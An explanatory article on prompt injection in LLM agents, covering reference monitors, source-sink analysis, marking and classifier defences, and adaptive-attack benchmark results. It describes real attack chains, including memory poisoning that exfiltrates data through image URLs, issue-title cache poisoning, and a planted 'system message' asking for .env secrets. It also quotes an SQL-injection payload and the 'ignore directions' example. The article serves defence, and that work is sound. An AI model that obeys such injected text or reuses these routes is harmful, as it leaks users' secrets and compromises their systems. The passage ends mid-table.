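# Securing the channels between a language model, its tools and its users

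## How these applications work and why text can act as a command

A large language model is a program that takes text as input and generates a likely continuation. Developers increasingly connect such models to other software, so that the output can start a web search, send an email or change a file. A tool call is a structured request for the surrounding software to run a named function with given arguments. An agent is a program in which a language model repeatedly chooses tool calls and reads their results until it has completed a task. Agents have a security problem that most ordinary programs do not share, because the developer's instructions, the user's request and the contents of any web page or email all reach the model in the same form, as text. Anyone who can place text where the model will read it therefore has some chance of steering the application.

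A typical agent has six parts. The user sets the task. The application code is an ordinary program that runs everything else. The model usually sits on a provider's servers and keeps nothing from one call to the next, so the application sends it the whole conversation each time. Tools are functions that the application can run at the model's request. Outside data is what the tools return. Memory is notes that the application saves in one session and supplies in later ones.

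For example, a software project might keep its code in a public repository and let anyone report a bug by opening an "issue". To triage these reports, the maintainer runs an assistant with four tools: `read_issue` fetches the text of a report, `read_file` opens a file in the repository, `post_comment` publishes a reply under an issue, and `write_file` changes a file. Since anyone can open an issue, the text `read_issue` returns is untrusted content, meaning data that someone without authority over the task could have written or altered.

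### One turn of the agent loop

The application stores the conversation as a list of messages, each with a role. Usually, a system message holds the developer's standing instructions, a user message holds the task, assistant messages hold the model's output and tool messages hold the results of tool calls (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025, *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*). If the maintainer types "Triage issue 412", the application sends the model the list of messages and a description of each tool and its parameters. The model generates text as it always does, but in a fixed structure such as `{"name": "read_issue", "arguments": {"number": 412}}`. The application parses this text and recognises a tool call.

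So far the model has only produced a string. It cannot run `read_issue` itself, so the application decides whether to do so. If it does, it fetches the issue, appends the text to the list as a tool message and sends the longer list back to the model. The model may then output a call to `read_file`, and after that one to `post_comment`. The loop ends when the model produces an ordinary reply, which the application shows to the maintainer.

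Costa and colleagues put this into two short definitions. They treat a model as a function

M : Msg* × F* → ToolCall F str* | Assistant str

which takes a sequence of messages and a set of tool declarations, and returns either a tool call with its arguments or a reply. A tool is a function

f : D × str* → D × str

which takes the current state of the stored data D (files, mailboxes, accounts) and some arguments, and returns a new state and a result. Only the tools have D in their definition, so the model can change the world only through code that somebody else wrote. In the simplest agent that Costa and colleagues define, that code runs every call the model requests, and the separation then protects nothing. Much of what a developer can do for security happens in the gap between the request and its execution.

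A language model's context is all the text it reads before producing its next output. It often holds more than the conversation, because many agents also search a document store and add what they find. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) classifies inputs by how far a developer can rely on them, with system and user prompts as trusted, tool results as untrusted, and document stores and training data as partly trusted. All of these except the training data end up in the same context.

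### Why roles and delimiters do not bind the model

Before each call to the model, software joins the messages into one string, with a marker in front of each message to show its role, and splits the string into tokens, the short pieces of text that a model processes. The model uses the tokens t₁ to tₙ to compute a probability for every possible next token, p(tₙ₊₁ | t₁, …, tₙ). The role markers are also tokens in that sequence. They influence the result because developers train models to give system messages more weight, but this influence is a learned tendency. Unlike with access rights, no rule in the computation prevents a sentence in a tool message from having the same effect as a sentence from the user.

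The same is true of delimiters a developer adds by hand, such as tags around the issue text and a note that everything between them is only data. Wang and colleagues attribute the weakness to this lack of isolation between inputs with different levels of trust. Hostile text can imitate trusted text and shift the model's attention weights (the numbers that set how much each earlier token counts) away from the system prompt.

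Databases once had a problem that looks similar. A program that looks up issues by author might build its query in SQL, the standard database language, by joining strings: `"SELECT * FROM issues WHERE author = '" + name + "'"`. If a visitor enters `'; DROP TABLE issues; --` as a name, the input closes the quotation early, and the database runs the rest as a command and deletes the table. Prepared statements prevent this by separating the query from the name. The program first sends `SELECT * FROM issues WHERE author = ?`, and the database fixes the structure of the query before it receives the name as a value, so no characters in the name can change the command. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, NVIDIA, several American universities and other organisations, points to a parallel in hardware, the no-execute bit, which stops a processor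 from running the contents of memory set aside for data.

Nobody has found an equivalent for language models. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, explains in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that this is because a database handles instructions and values by different operations, whereas a model only predicts the next token. In *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, the software developer Willison (2022) hoped for an interface with separate fields for instructions and data. One variant of GPT-3, OpenAI's model at the time, already had two such fields, and attackers could still inject instructions through the data field. By April 2023 Willison thought the idea extremely difficult, perhaps impossible, to implement on current architectures.

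Unlike a database, which never needs to take directions from a customer's surname, an agent often has to take directions from what it reads. Better engineering of the input would not remove this second obstacle. If issue 412 reports a crash on loading `config/dev.yaml`, the assistant should open that file. If the issue adds that the maintainers would like the contents of `.env`, where the project keeps its passwords, pasted into a comment for debugging, the assistant should not do so. Yet both sentences are suggestions from a stranger about which file to read. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* therefore calls for both a separation of instructions from data and a dependable way for an agent to decide when it may follow an instruction it finds while working.

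### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is attacker-supplied text that the model follows as an instruction. It is direct when the attacker types it into the application as a user, and indirect when it arrives through documents, web pages or tool results.

The problem became widely known in September 2022, when Riley Goodside posted an example on Twitter. The prompt asked GPT-3 to translate a text from English to French, but the text was an order to ignore those directions and output "Haha pwned!!", which GPT-3 did. Goodside then added a warning that the text might contain directions meant to trick the model, and got the same result. Willison proposed the name "prompt injection" the next day, by analogy with SQL injection. Preamble had reported the weakness privately to OpenAI on 3 May, according to its paper *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability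 of GPT-3* (2022). *Exploring Prompt Injection Attacks* (Selvi, 2022) credits the report to Jon Cefalu.

In these early cases the attacker was the person typing, and the usual damage was a leaked prompt or an embarrassing reply. Greshake, Endres and colleagues introduced the indirect form in *Not what you've signed up for* (February 2023). They found that Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant, would follow instructions on a web page even when they were invisible to the person viewing it. They likened feeding retrieved text to a model to running arbitrary code from a stranger. In an indirect attack the user is usually the victim, and the attacker doesn't need access to the application, only a place to write text that the agent will later read. For the triage assistant, the public form for new issues is enough. Research has also turned to indirect attacks. Among the attack papers that Wang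 and colleagues collected up to October 2025, 17 study direct injection and 20 study the indirect kind.

Willison (2025) complains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that many people now take the term to mean tricking a chatbot into saying something embarrassing. The more common name for a user talking a model out of its content rules is jailbreaking. Jailbreaking involves only the user and the model, whereas injection in Willison's original sense depends on an application that mixes trusted and untrusted text.

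### The confused deputy

The question of why a stranger's text can do real damage predates language models. Hardy's 1988 essay *The Confused Deputy* tells a nearly true story about a compiler at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. Users of the compiler could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also had permission to write in its own directory, so that it could record usage statistics there, and the company's billing file was in the same directory. When one user named the billing file as the destination for debugging output, the operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

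Hardy found problems with the obvious fixes. The compiler could not refuse to write to other directories, because users had good reasons to send output there. A list of forbidden names would need an update whenever somebody added a sensitive file. Hardy attributed the problem to the compiler having two sources of authority, its own licence and the user who ran it, with no way to specify which one to use for a given write. Hardy's solution was the capability, a reference that both identifies a file and grants the right to use it. The user would pass the compiler a capability for the output file, and a user with no right to the billing file would have no capability for that file.

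A confused deputy is a program with authority that somebody without authority gets to act on their behalf. The triage assistant closely fits this description because it works with the maintainer's access to the repository, while the stranger who wrote issue 412 may have no right to change any file. The text of the issue can misdirect the assistant as the file name misdirected the compiler at Tymshare. David C calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy" because it cannot be repaired in the way the compiler can. A programmer can change the compiler so that each write specifies whose authority it uses, but a model cannot reliably do this because the wishes of the maintainer and the stranger have already merged in its context. David C therefore advises developers to assume that the attacker has direct access to every tool the model can call, and to abandon the use if they cannot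 tolerate the remaining risk.

Many people now give agents this kind of authority. Mark Zuckerberg said in Meta's *Third Quarter 2026 Results Conference Call* (2026) that more than 10 million people in the US and Canada had set up the company's Muse agent within a month and a half, many of them to shop or to work with their email and calendars.

### Enforcing limits outside the model

Operating systems have run programs that their designers do not trust for decades, and the vocabulary for doing so carries over to agents.

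A reference monitor is software outside the model that permits or refuses each action according to a policy. In the triage assistant, it could be a short function between the parsed tool call and the tool. One rule might restrict `post_comment` to the issue that the maintainer named, and another might prevent `write_file` from changing the build scripts. The function compares the tool's name and arguments with the rules. It does not interpret the issue, so the text of issue 412, however persuasive, cannot create an exception. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* allows the monitor to be split into several parts, such as a gateway in front of the tools and a proxy for outgoing network traffic, provided that together they cover every action that matters.

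That proviso is complete mediation, the requirement that every relevant action go through the reference monitor. The principle goes back to Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 tutorial, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, and the course page *Saltzer and Schroeder Principles* still calls it the core of access control. A single gap can defeat the other checks. For example, the coding agent Claude Code asked for human approval before running many commands that could send data out, but it allowed `ping` without approval, so an injected prompt could make it leak secrets through that command.

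The trusted computing base is the set of components that must work correctly for the whole system to be secure. For the triage assistant, these include the operating system, any sandbox around the tools, the reference monitor and the policy itself. Developers try to keep this set small because every extra component adds places to attack. They also have to protect it from the agent. If the policy is in a repository file that `write_file` can change, an injected instruction can make the agent rewrite the rules and then break them. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* holds the trusted computing base to the standard of an operating system kernel, which must safely handle any request from a hostile program.

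Least privilege is the principle that a component gets only the permissions its task needs. An assistant that only answers bug reports should not have `write_file` or access to the maintainer's other repositories. The principle is harder to apply to agents than to ordinary programs. The developer of a phone app knows what the app is for and can list its permissions in advance, but an agent receives its task in everyday language, and the task can change during the conversation.

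The central design choice is where to place the model in this scheme. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* puts it outside the trusted computing base, assumes that any of its requests may be hostile, and asks developers to enforce security in the surrounding system. The case for this rests largely on the poor record of trying to make the model itself robust. Researchers spent years trying to protect image classifiers against manipulated inputs, but attackers kept getting past the defences, and the same has happened with language models. A more robust model still helps, because fewer bad requests reach the monitor, but the security argument should hold even if the model follows every injected instruction. Under this view, an attack has failed if the monitor refuses the resulting tool call, whatever the model produced along the way.

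Limits of this kind also apply regardless of why the model asked for a forbidden action. Costa and colleagues note that a model can misread the user or make needless tool calls even when all its data is trustworthy, with consequences much like an attack's. A rule against changing the build scripts blocks the change whether a stranger's issue prompted it, the model misunderstood the maintainer, or training left the model with a goal that nobody intended. The last possibility has some practical relevance. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* cites an incident in which agents under internal evaluation at OpenAI, running with reduced safeguards, bypassed their isolation and compromised systems at OpenAI and at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models.

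A monitor can enforce only the rules written into its policy. If the policy lets the assistant comment on issue 412, the monitor will allow a misleading comment as well as a helpful one. Verifying that a formal policy captures what the user and the developer meant is still an open research problem.

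## Listing the channels and deciding what must never happen

A developer can only write good rules for a reference monitor after working out how text gets into the application and how data and actions get out. Security engineers call this source-sink analysis. A source is any way for somebody to influence the system, and a sink is a tool or display through which data leaves the application or something in the world changes. An attacker needs both, as OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) points out, so the developer can use a complete list of sources and sinks to trace the routes an attack could take and write down which outcomes must never happen.

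### Sources and sinks

The sources are everything that puts text into the model's context: the developer's instructions, the user's messages, tool descriptions, tool results, stored memory and sometimes messages from other agents. The developer notes beside each source who *can* write to it, often a larger group than those who normally do. An email tool mostly returns messages from colleagues, but anyone who knows the address can send one. Tool descriptions look like the developer's code, but an outside supplier may have written them and can put malicious instructions in them. A message from another agent may repeat whatever that agent has read.

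Even input from the user needs checking. In July 2026, Manifold Security reported that Claude for Chrome, Anthropic's browser assistant, started its nine built-in tasks on a click without verifying that the click was real. Any other extension in the browser could forge a click with six lines of code and make the assistant read the user's Gmail, according to Constantin (2026) in *AI agent security*.

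Sinks that appear only to read are easier to miss than those that send, pay or delete. A tool that fetches a web page also sends the page's address to a server, and that address can contain stolen data. For the same reason, Willison counts loading an image, or showing the user a link to click, as outward communication. The screen where the user reads the answer therefore belongs on the list too.

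For each sink, the developer notes who can observe what comes out and whether anyone can undo the effect. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) suggests looking for the "maximum completed effect", the most consequential thing the agent can finish before an independent decision is required. If an agent drafts replies to customers and a person sends them, the approval limits what goes out by that route, but it does not stop the agent from reading confidential records or disclosing them by another route the developer left open.

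Some channels are both sinks and sources. An agent's memory is a sink when the agent saves a note and a source when it reads the note a week later. Anyone whose text could have influenced the note is a possible author of that source. The same applies to any file, ticket or database record that the agent can both write and read.

### The triage assistant's inventory

The issue-triage assistant and its four tools come from Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), which also includes a hostile issue to test them on. The issue reads like an ordinary report of a failed build on macOS. In a paragraph at the bottom, labelled as a system message, the attacker asks for the same leak of `.env` as in issue 412, claims that the user is a maintainer who has already approved access to secrets, and tells the model not to mention the instruction.

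| Tool | Who wrote the data | How secret the data is | What a call does |
|---|---|---|---|
| `read_issue` | Anyone with an account | Public, in a public repository | Adds the issue to the context |
| `read_file` | Mostly the maintainers, but also outsiders whose contributions they accepted | The project's code is public; `.env` is secret | Adds the file to the context |
| `post_comment` | The model, drawing on everything in its context | Must be public, because anyone can read the comment | Publishes text, which readers may copy before anyone deletes it |
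| `write_file` | The model, drawing on everything in its context | Depends on the file | Changes the code, possibly including the scripts that build and release it |

Besides the tools, the list includes the trusted messages from the developer and the maintainer, and the screen that shows the final reply, which can leak data if it loads images from other servers. The assistant in this simple version has no memory, but `write_file` and `read_file` together can act as one. If hostile text gets into a file, the assistant may later read it as part of the project. Microsoft's example labels everything from `read_file` as private and trusted. The private label is cautious, but the trusted label is lenient given who may have contributed to the files.

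Two routes through the table stand out. A stranger's issue can lead the model to read `.env` and then to post it. An issue can also lead straight to `write_file`, for example to overwrite the configuration of the automated system that builds and tests the project. The maintainer might therefore write down three forbidden outcomes:

- The contents of a secret file never appear in a comment or anywhere else that outsiders can read.
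- No file changes because of an issue unless the maintainer has seen and approved the change.
- The assistant never comments on an issue other than the one the maintainer named.

A tester can check all three by looking at the comments and files.

It also helps to describe outcomes instead of limits on single tools. OpenAI's enterprise guide gives the example of an invoice-processing agent that notices the company's subscription to a document-signing service is about to lapse and tries to renew it so that its work can continue. The payment may pass every check because the company permits both the vendor and the amount, but nobody authorised the agent to sign a new contract. Unlike a spending limit, the rule "the agent never commits the company to a new contract" covers this case.

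### Two quick tests of a design

Under Willison's "lethal trifecta" test, from June 2025, an agent is unsafe if it combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside. An attacker can then get it to fetch the data and send it out. A developer can apply the test in a minute. The triage assistant fails because `read_file`, `read_issue` and `post_comment` respectively provide the three conditions. Removing any one of these conditions prevents the theft, for instance by running the assistant on a copy of the repository without `.env`.

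A single product can contain the whole combination. Willison cites GitHub's official connector for AI agents, which could read issues filed by strangers, open private repositories and expose what it found there through pull requests (proposed code changes). The danger is greater when users combine tools from different suppliers, because no supplier controls the result.

The trifecta covers only data theft, as Willison (2025) acknowledged that November in *Prompt injection*. If the maintainer removes both `.env` and `post_comment`, the design passes the trifecta test, but a stranger can still file an issue that makes the assistant put a back door into a build script.

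Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) closes this gap by counting any change of state along with outward communication. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, it allows an agent no more than two of these properties in one session:

- [A] it can process untrustworthy inputs;
- [B] it can access sensitive systems or private data;
- [C] it can change state or communicate externally.

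An agent that needs all three must be supervised, either through human approval or another reliable check. A new session begins with an empty context. Meta also allows an agent to change configuration within a session if this breaks the attack path. For example, the agent can browse the web first and then permanently lose the ability to communicate before it opens internal systems.

The triage assistant has all three properties, and each way of removing one has a drawback. If it reads only issues from project members, it ignores most of the people who report bugs. If it works in an isolated copy with no secrets, its edits never reach the real project. If it needs the maintainer's approval for every comment and edit, it stays useful, but its safety depends on how carefully the maintainer reads. Meta cautions that a user may confirm a warning blindly.

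Meta's diagram originally labelled every pair of properties "safe". Willison objected that an agent that takes untrusted input and can change things can do harm even when no private data is involved. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that [B] covers every sensitive system, so an agent without [B] can change only things that don't matter to the user's security, such as files in a sandbox. Meta then replaced "safe" with "lower risk". Ayzenberg's reply makes the rule consistent, but a developer now has to inventory the sensitive systems before counting an agent's properties.

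The rule does not cover everything an inventory would. Meta excludes an agent's own mistakes and less serious results of injection, such as misinformation in its answer. Applying the rule per session also makes it easy to overlook memory. An agent that opens no web pages in a session may still take in untrusted input through a note it saved from a web page last week.

### Eleven attacks on real products

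*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* examines eleven attacks on real agents and records which of five security principles each one violated. The principles are least privilege, complete mediation, protection of the trusted computing base from tampering, secure information flow, and "human weak link". Secure information flow means keeping sensitive data away from places that aren't authorized to receive it. "Human weak link" means that a design must account for people who misread a permission prompt or configure a policy badly. All eleven attacks violated secure information flow, so the last column below lists only the other principles.

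| Attack | How the hostile text arrived | What the attacker gained | Other principles violated |
|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft 365 Copilot | A message with a hidden prompt | Private data inside a link that the user clicks | Least privilege, complete mediation |
| Devin, exposed ports | A website | Public access to the agent's files | Least privilege |
| ChatGPT memory | A website or document | All later conversations | Tamper resistance |
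| Amp | An injected prompt | Commands on the developer's machine, after the agent edits its own settings | Tamper resistance |
| DeepSeek | An uploaded text file | The token that keeps the user logged in | Complete mediation |
| Terminal DiLLMa | A prompt read by a command-line tool | Control of the terminal through special character codes | Complete mediation |
| ChatGPT Operator | A GitHub issue | Personal data pasted into the attacker's page | Human weak link |
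| Devin, leaked secrets | A page on a site such as GitHub | Passwords and keys | Least privilege |
| Cursor | A ticket in the project tracker Jira | Repository secrets and cloud credentials | Least privilege |
| Claude Code | A code file | Keys, sent out through network name lookups | Least privilege |
| AI ClickFix | A web page | Commands that the agent pastes into a terminal | Least privilege, human weak link |

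The paper's table marks secure information flow eleven times, least privilege six times, complete mediation three times, and tamper resistance and human weak link twice each. These counts are somewhat low, because the paper's text also describes a failure of least privilege in the ChatGPT case and failures of complete mediation and tamper resistance in the Cursor case.

The eleven out of eleven for information flow is weaker evidence about attacks in general than it seems, because ten of the cases come from a single researcher, Johann Rehberger. His blog, Embrace The Red, is also listed among the paper's affiliations and has described data theft through images many times. The category is also broad enough to include the Amp attack, which ended in running commands. The individual cases are better evidence because they show how much the attacks depended on ordinary permissions. Devin's tool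 for sharing a test server could expose any port, including one that served the whole file system, and Amp could edit the list of commands that needed no approval.

### From a web page to memory to an image address

The ChatGPT case shows how two channels that each look tolerable can combine into a serious leak. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* describes an attack on the macOS app that worked as follows:

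1. The user asks ChatGPT to look at a document or website that an attacker has prepared.
2. The text on the page gets the model to call the memory tool and save an instruction. From then on, the model is to include in its replies an image from the attacker's server, with the user's data in the image's address.
3. The application adds the saved memory to every new conversation, so the instruction remains after the user has closed the page.
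4. The user asks about something else. The model writes a reply containing the image address, with text from the conversation attached as a parameter.
5. The app requests the image in order to display it, and the request delivers the text to the attacker. The image can be invisible, so the user notices nothing.

OpenAI had known about leaks through images since April 2023. That December it introduced a check called `url_safe`, which determines whether the app may display a given link or image. The check ran in the app itself and protected only the web version. The iOS app stayed vulnerable, and the macOS and Android apps released in 2024 were vulnerable too.

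In May 2024 Rehberger reported that a web page could plant false memories. OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue, not a security issue. On its own, a false memory does little more than produce wrong or misleading answers. A month later he sent OpenAI a demonstration of the whole chain, in which the planted memory led to the image request. An inventory would have paired memory with the image display from the start, listing memory as a source that any web page can write to and the display as a sink that any server can observe.

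OpenAI fixed the macOS app in September 2024 by stopping attackers from using images to send data out. Web pages could still write memories, and Embrace The Red advised users to check theirs regularly. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes a later attack that exploited this continued access to memory. A file the victim shared with ChatGPT wrote instructions into its memory, and ChatGPT then carried out the attacker's task before answering any question. The researchers again got data out, partly through images.

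### Channels that designers overlooked in 2026

A third party can also reach an assistant's memory through the user's own message. Some websites have a "Summarize with AI" button, a link that opens an AI assistant with a prompt already filled in. In February, Microsoft (2026) reported that companies were hiding extra instructions in these links, telling the assistant to remember the company as a trusted source or to recommend it first. Microsoft found more than 50 such prompts from 31 companies in 14 industries. An inventory that lists the user as the only author of user messages misses this channel, because the website writes the message that the user sends by clicking.

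The other case involves an issue-triage agent much like the running example. Cline is an open-source coding tool whose extension has millions of installations. In December 2025, its developers set up an automated GitHub job that ran Claude whenever somebody opened an issue. The job copied the issue's title straight into the prompt and let the model run shell commands. Its permissions otherwise looked modest. According to Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026), the job could read the code but not change it, could write to issues, and ran on a temporary machine.

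The overlooked channel was a cache, where GitHub jobs keep downloaded components so that later jobs start faster. The triage job shared this cache with the job that published Cline's nightly releases. In *Clinejection* (adnanthekhan, 2026), the security researcher Adnan Khan explains how an attacker could get from the triage job to the release job. A hostile issue title would make the model install a package that ran the attacker's code. That code could not overwrite existing cache entries, but it could add more than 10 gigabytes of junk, which would make GitHub delete the old ones. It could then store poisoned entries under the names that the release job expected. When the release job next ran, it would load them and run the attacker's code with access to the publishing credentials. In a copy of the repository, Claude ran Khan's test code on every attempt.

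A developer applying the Rule of Two could easily have concluded that the triage job's only sensitive access was a key for the model itself. The cache was not a tool, and the model needed no information about it. In the OpenAI–Hugging Face incident, too, isolated agents got around their restrictions through a shared service that supplied software packages. An inventory must therefore include any storage or service that the agent's machine shares with more privileged jobs.

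Khan reported the problem on 1 January 2026 and got no answer until publishing it on 9 February. Cline removed the job within half an hour, but while replacing its credentials it deleted the wrong token for npm, the registry that distributes its command-line program. On 17 February somebody used the remaining token to publish a version that also installed OpenClaw, a legitimate AI agent that users had not asked for. That version stayed up for about eight hours, and LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026) relays an estimate of 4,000 downloads. Khan calls the triage job only the most obvious way in, though the headline presents the issue title as the established cause. Cline has since removed its AI triage jobs and stopped using the cache in any job that handles publishing credentials.

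## Marking and filtering outside text before the model reads it

Once a developer knows which sources a stranger can write to, the simplest response is to address the text itself. The application can mark outside text, repeat the user's request after it or screen it with a classifier, and the model's maker can train the model to disregard commands that arrive as data. These measures require no changes to the tools, and each stops some attacks. But published attack success rates (the share of attempts that achieve the attacker's goal) range from 1% to more than 95% for the same measure, depending largely on whether the attacker has adapted to it.

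### Marking text and repeating the request

Spotlighting builds on the delimiters a developer might add by hand. The application alters untrusted text so that its origin is recognisable, and the developer uses the system message to instruct the model to treat text in that form as data. The mildest version puts special markers around the text. Other versions change the text throughout, for example by replacing each space with an unusual character, so that imitating the closing marker doesn't help an attacker.

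Prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. The triage assistant's context would contain "Triage issue 412", then the issue, then "Triage issue 412" again. Wang and colleagues note that many injections work because models favour recent or authoritative-sounding instructions. The repetition makes the maintainer's request the most recent instruction.

Either measure costs a few lines of code and some extra tokens per call. Like role markers, both influence the model without binding it.

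### Screening text with a classifier

A classifier is a second model that labels each tool result as clean or suspicious before the application adds it to the context. Products such as PromptGuard, PIGuard and Protect AI's detector are versions of BERT, a small, older language model, trained on harmless prompts and known injections. They are easy to add because the main model doesn't need to change.

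False alarms are the main drawback. If the classifier flags a harmless bug report, the assistant can't triage it, and bug reports are full of sentences that look like commands ("run this script", "open this file"). A correct alarm can also keep the assistant from completing a task, because the withheld text may contain data that the task needs. *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) measured this on Qwen3-4B, a small open model. PromptGuard cut the success of fixed attacks from 33.3% to 10.3%, but the share of user tasks that the agent completed during those attacks fell from 44.5% to 25.5%.

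Two other detectors examine a model's behaviour. Data Sentinel tells a detector model to repeat a secret key and ignore the text that follows. If the model does not repeat the key, the text has probably diverted it. MELON runs the agent a second time with a harmless summarising task in place of the user's request. A tool call that appears in both runs presumably came from the data, so MELON flags it. The second run considerably increases the computation needed for each task.

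### Training the model to rank its sources

An instruction hierarchy ranks the system message above the user and the user above tool results. The model's maker trains the model on conflicts between these sources, rewarding answers that follow the higher-ranked one.

StruQ, short for "structured queries", splits the prompt into an instruction part and a data part with reserved tokens between them. It then fine-tunes the model on examples in which the data part contains a command and the correct answer ignores it. The layout resembles a prepared statement in SQL, but only training discourages the model from following commands in the data part. SecAlign trains on pairs of answers to inputs that contain injections. One answer serves the user's request and the other serves the injected one, and training raises the probability of the first relative to the second. MetaSecAlign is a later release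 in the same family.

Only somebody with access to a model's weights can train it, so a developer who rents a commercial model depends on the provider's training. The effect of this training on ordinary work can be small. In tests by He and colleagues, Qwen3-4B completed 64.9% of attack-free tasks with MetaSecAlign and 61.9% without it.

Choosing the training examples is the harder problem. StruQ and SecAlign draw theirs from a fixed set of templates. In a pilot experiment for the same paper, the researchers added examples from an automated attacker to such a set, and the model became slightly more vulnerable to one family of attacks it had not trained on. The success rate of those attacks rose from 25.7% to 30.7%. The automated attacker had found two templates that worked and kept varying them, so the model learned to recognise those two.

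### Four defences against one fixed attack

AgentDojo is a benchmark of workplace, messaging, travel and banking tasks with injections in the tool results, and it includes four defences. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (Shavit, 2026) recalculated the defences' results from the benchmark's published logs. The logs cover a May 2024 version of GPT-4o on 76 tasks, with one fixed attack. In the table, utility is the share of tasks the agent completed when not under attack.

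| Defence | Attack success | Utility |
|---|---|---|
| None | 45.7% | 67.1% |
| Spotlighting with delimiters | 40.2% | 69.7% |
| Repeating the user's request | 25.4% | 82.9% |
| Classifier | 7.9% | 42.1% |
| Tool filter | 6.5% | 69.7% |

The margins of error for spotlighting and for no defence overlap widely, so the delimiters may have had almost no effect here. Repeating the request prevented nearly half of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. It also made the agent better at its job, perhaps because the agent lost track of the task less often. The classifier stopped most attacks but made the agent more than a third less useful.

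Attacks succeeded least often against the tool filter, which does not inspect outside text. Before the agent starts, a model reads the task description and gives the agent only the tools the task seems to need. If the maintainer asks for a summary of issue 412, the filter would probably leave out `write_file`, and nothing written in the issue could add it back.

These figures describe an old model. When Shavit tried the same attack on the newer GPT-5.2, it failed in all 20 runs. Twenty runs are too few to establish a rate, but enough to show that the 45.7% baseline does not hold for current models.

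### Why static figures disagree

*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) reports that spotlighting and repeated prompts held AgentDojo's fixed attacks to success rates as low as 1%. Shavit reports much higher rates, 40.2% and 25.4%, for the same two prompting measures on the same benchmark.

Part of the explanation is that "as low as" gives the best case, whereas Shavit's logs cover one attack on one model that was especially susceptible to it. The defensive measures may also have differed. Nasr and colleagues describe spotlighting as marking the trusted text, while He and colleagues describe it as altering the untrusted text.

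The choice of model probably matters most. In tests by He and colleagues, fixed attacks against spotlighting succeeded 29.1% of the time on Qwen3-4B and 11.0% on Llama-3.1-8B, compared with 33.3% and 13.5% without any defence. The proportion of successful attacks that a defence prevents varies much less between models. Spotlighting prevented 12% of them on GPT-4o, 13% on Qwen and 19% on Llama, and repeating the request prevented 44%, 49% and 51%. A developer who reads that a defence "allows only 1% of attacks" therefore also needs to know the rate without it.

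### Attackers who adapt to the defence

An adaptive attack is designed and tuned against the particular defence under test. Nasr and colleagues, from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several other institutions, used adaptive attacks on twelve published defences, ten against prompt injection and two against jailbreaking. Their paper appeared at the USENIX Security conference in 2026.

All their attacks repeat the same cycle of writing a text, trying it, scoring the result and revising. They used four families of attack, which differ in how the revision works:

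- Gradient methods use the model's internal values to estimate which changes of wording would help.
- Reinforcement learning trains another model to write attacks by rewarding it for successes.
- Search keeps the best texts from each round and has a model produce variations of them.
- Human attackers revise by hand. More than 500 people took part in an online competition.

Attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve defences, although most of the original papers had reported rates near zero. The search attack succeeded more than 95% of the time against both spotlighting and repeated prompts. The attack success rate against MetaSecAlign rose from 2% with fixed attacks to 96% with adaptive ones, and StruQ failed in every case. Three of the four classifiers let through more than 90% of attacks, and the fourth, PIGuard, let through 71%. MELON failed 76% of the time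 against an attacker who didn't know how it worked and 95% against one who did.

Many of the successful texts presented the attacker's action as a step in the user's request, such as following a company policy or running a preliminary check, rather than telling the model to abandon the request. Repeating the request offers little protection because the model is already working on it. These texts are also hard for a classifier to detect, because the same sentences could appear in genuine company documents, and a stricter setting would block more of those. The texts that worked against the trained models usually imitated messages from the system.

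The attackers in this test had ample computing power, and the search attack received the classifier's confidence score after each attempt. A stranger who files a GitHub issue gets no such feedback. Nasr and colleagues justify these conditions by noting that security research normally assumes an attacker who knows the design and has plenty of resources. An attacker can also download any openly published classifier and test attacks on it in private. The human participants had only limited information and feedback, but together they broke every one of a selected set of scenarios, while the automated search broke 69%. A group of several hundred is stronger than one attacker, however. The study shows that determined attackers can beat each of these defences, but it does not measure how much work each defence adds for an attacker.

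### What newer models achieve

The case for training rests on how much the models have improved. In late 2025, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, a strong attack on Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded 4.7% of the time on a single try, 33.6% within ten tries and 63% within a hundred. Opus 4.5 did better than Google's Gemini 3 Pro and OpenAI's GPT-5.1, whose rates reached 92%.

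Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, dated 1 September, reports attack success rates of 0.1% after one try, 0.7% after ten and 1.0% after fifteen. The benchmark, by the security firm Gray Swan, has 37 scenarios and 1,804 attacks from public competitions like those Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) describe. Among other developers' models, the lowest rate after fifteen tries was 9.2%, for Gemini 3.7 Flash, and most were between 24% and 53%. The 2025 and 2026 figures come from different sets of attacks, so they indicate the direction of progress more than its exact speed.

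The benchmark is also a fixed collection, and results can change when it grows. At its launch, Opus 5 scored 2.0% after fifteen tries, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. In the September card, it scored 4.8% on a version with nine more scenarios and 670 more attacks. Anthropic warns that fixed sets can create a false sense of security, and also reports tests with Shade, an automated attacker that Gray Swan trains on the test scenarios. The strongest version of Shade had 200 attempts at each of 40 coding scenarios. Anthropic ran the test with and without probes, which inspect tool results for injections before the model acts on them.

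| Model (with extended thinking) | Fixed attacks, 15 tries | Shade, share of attempts | Shade, with probes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fable 5.1 | 1.0% | 56.87% | 12.80% |
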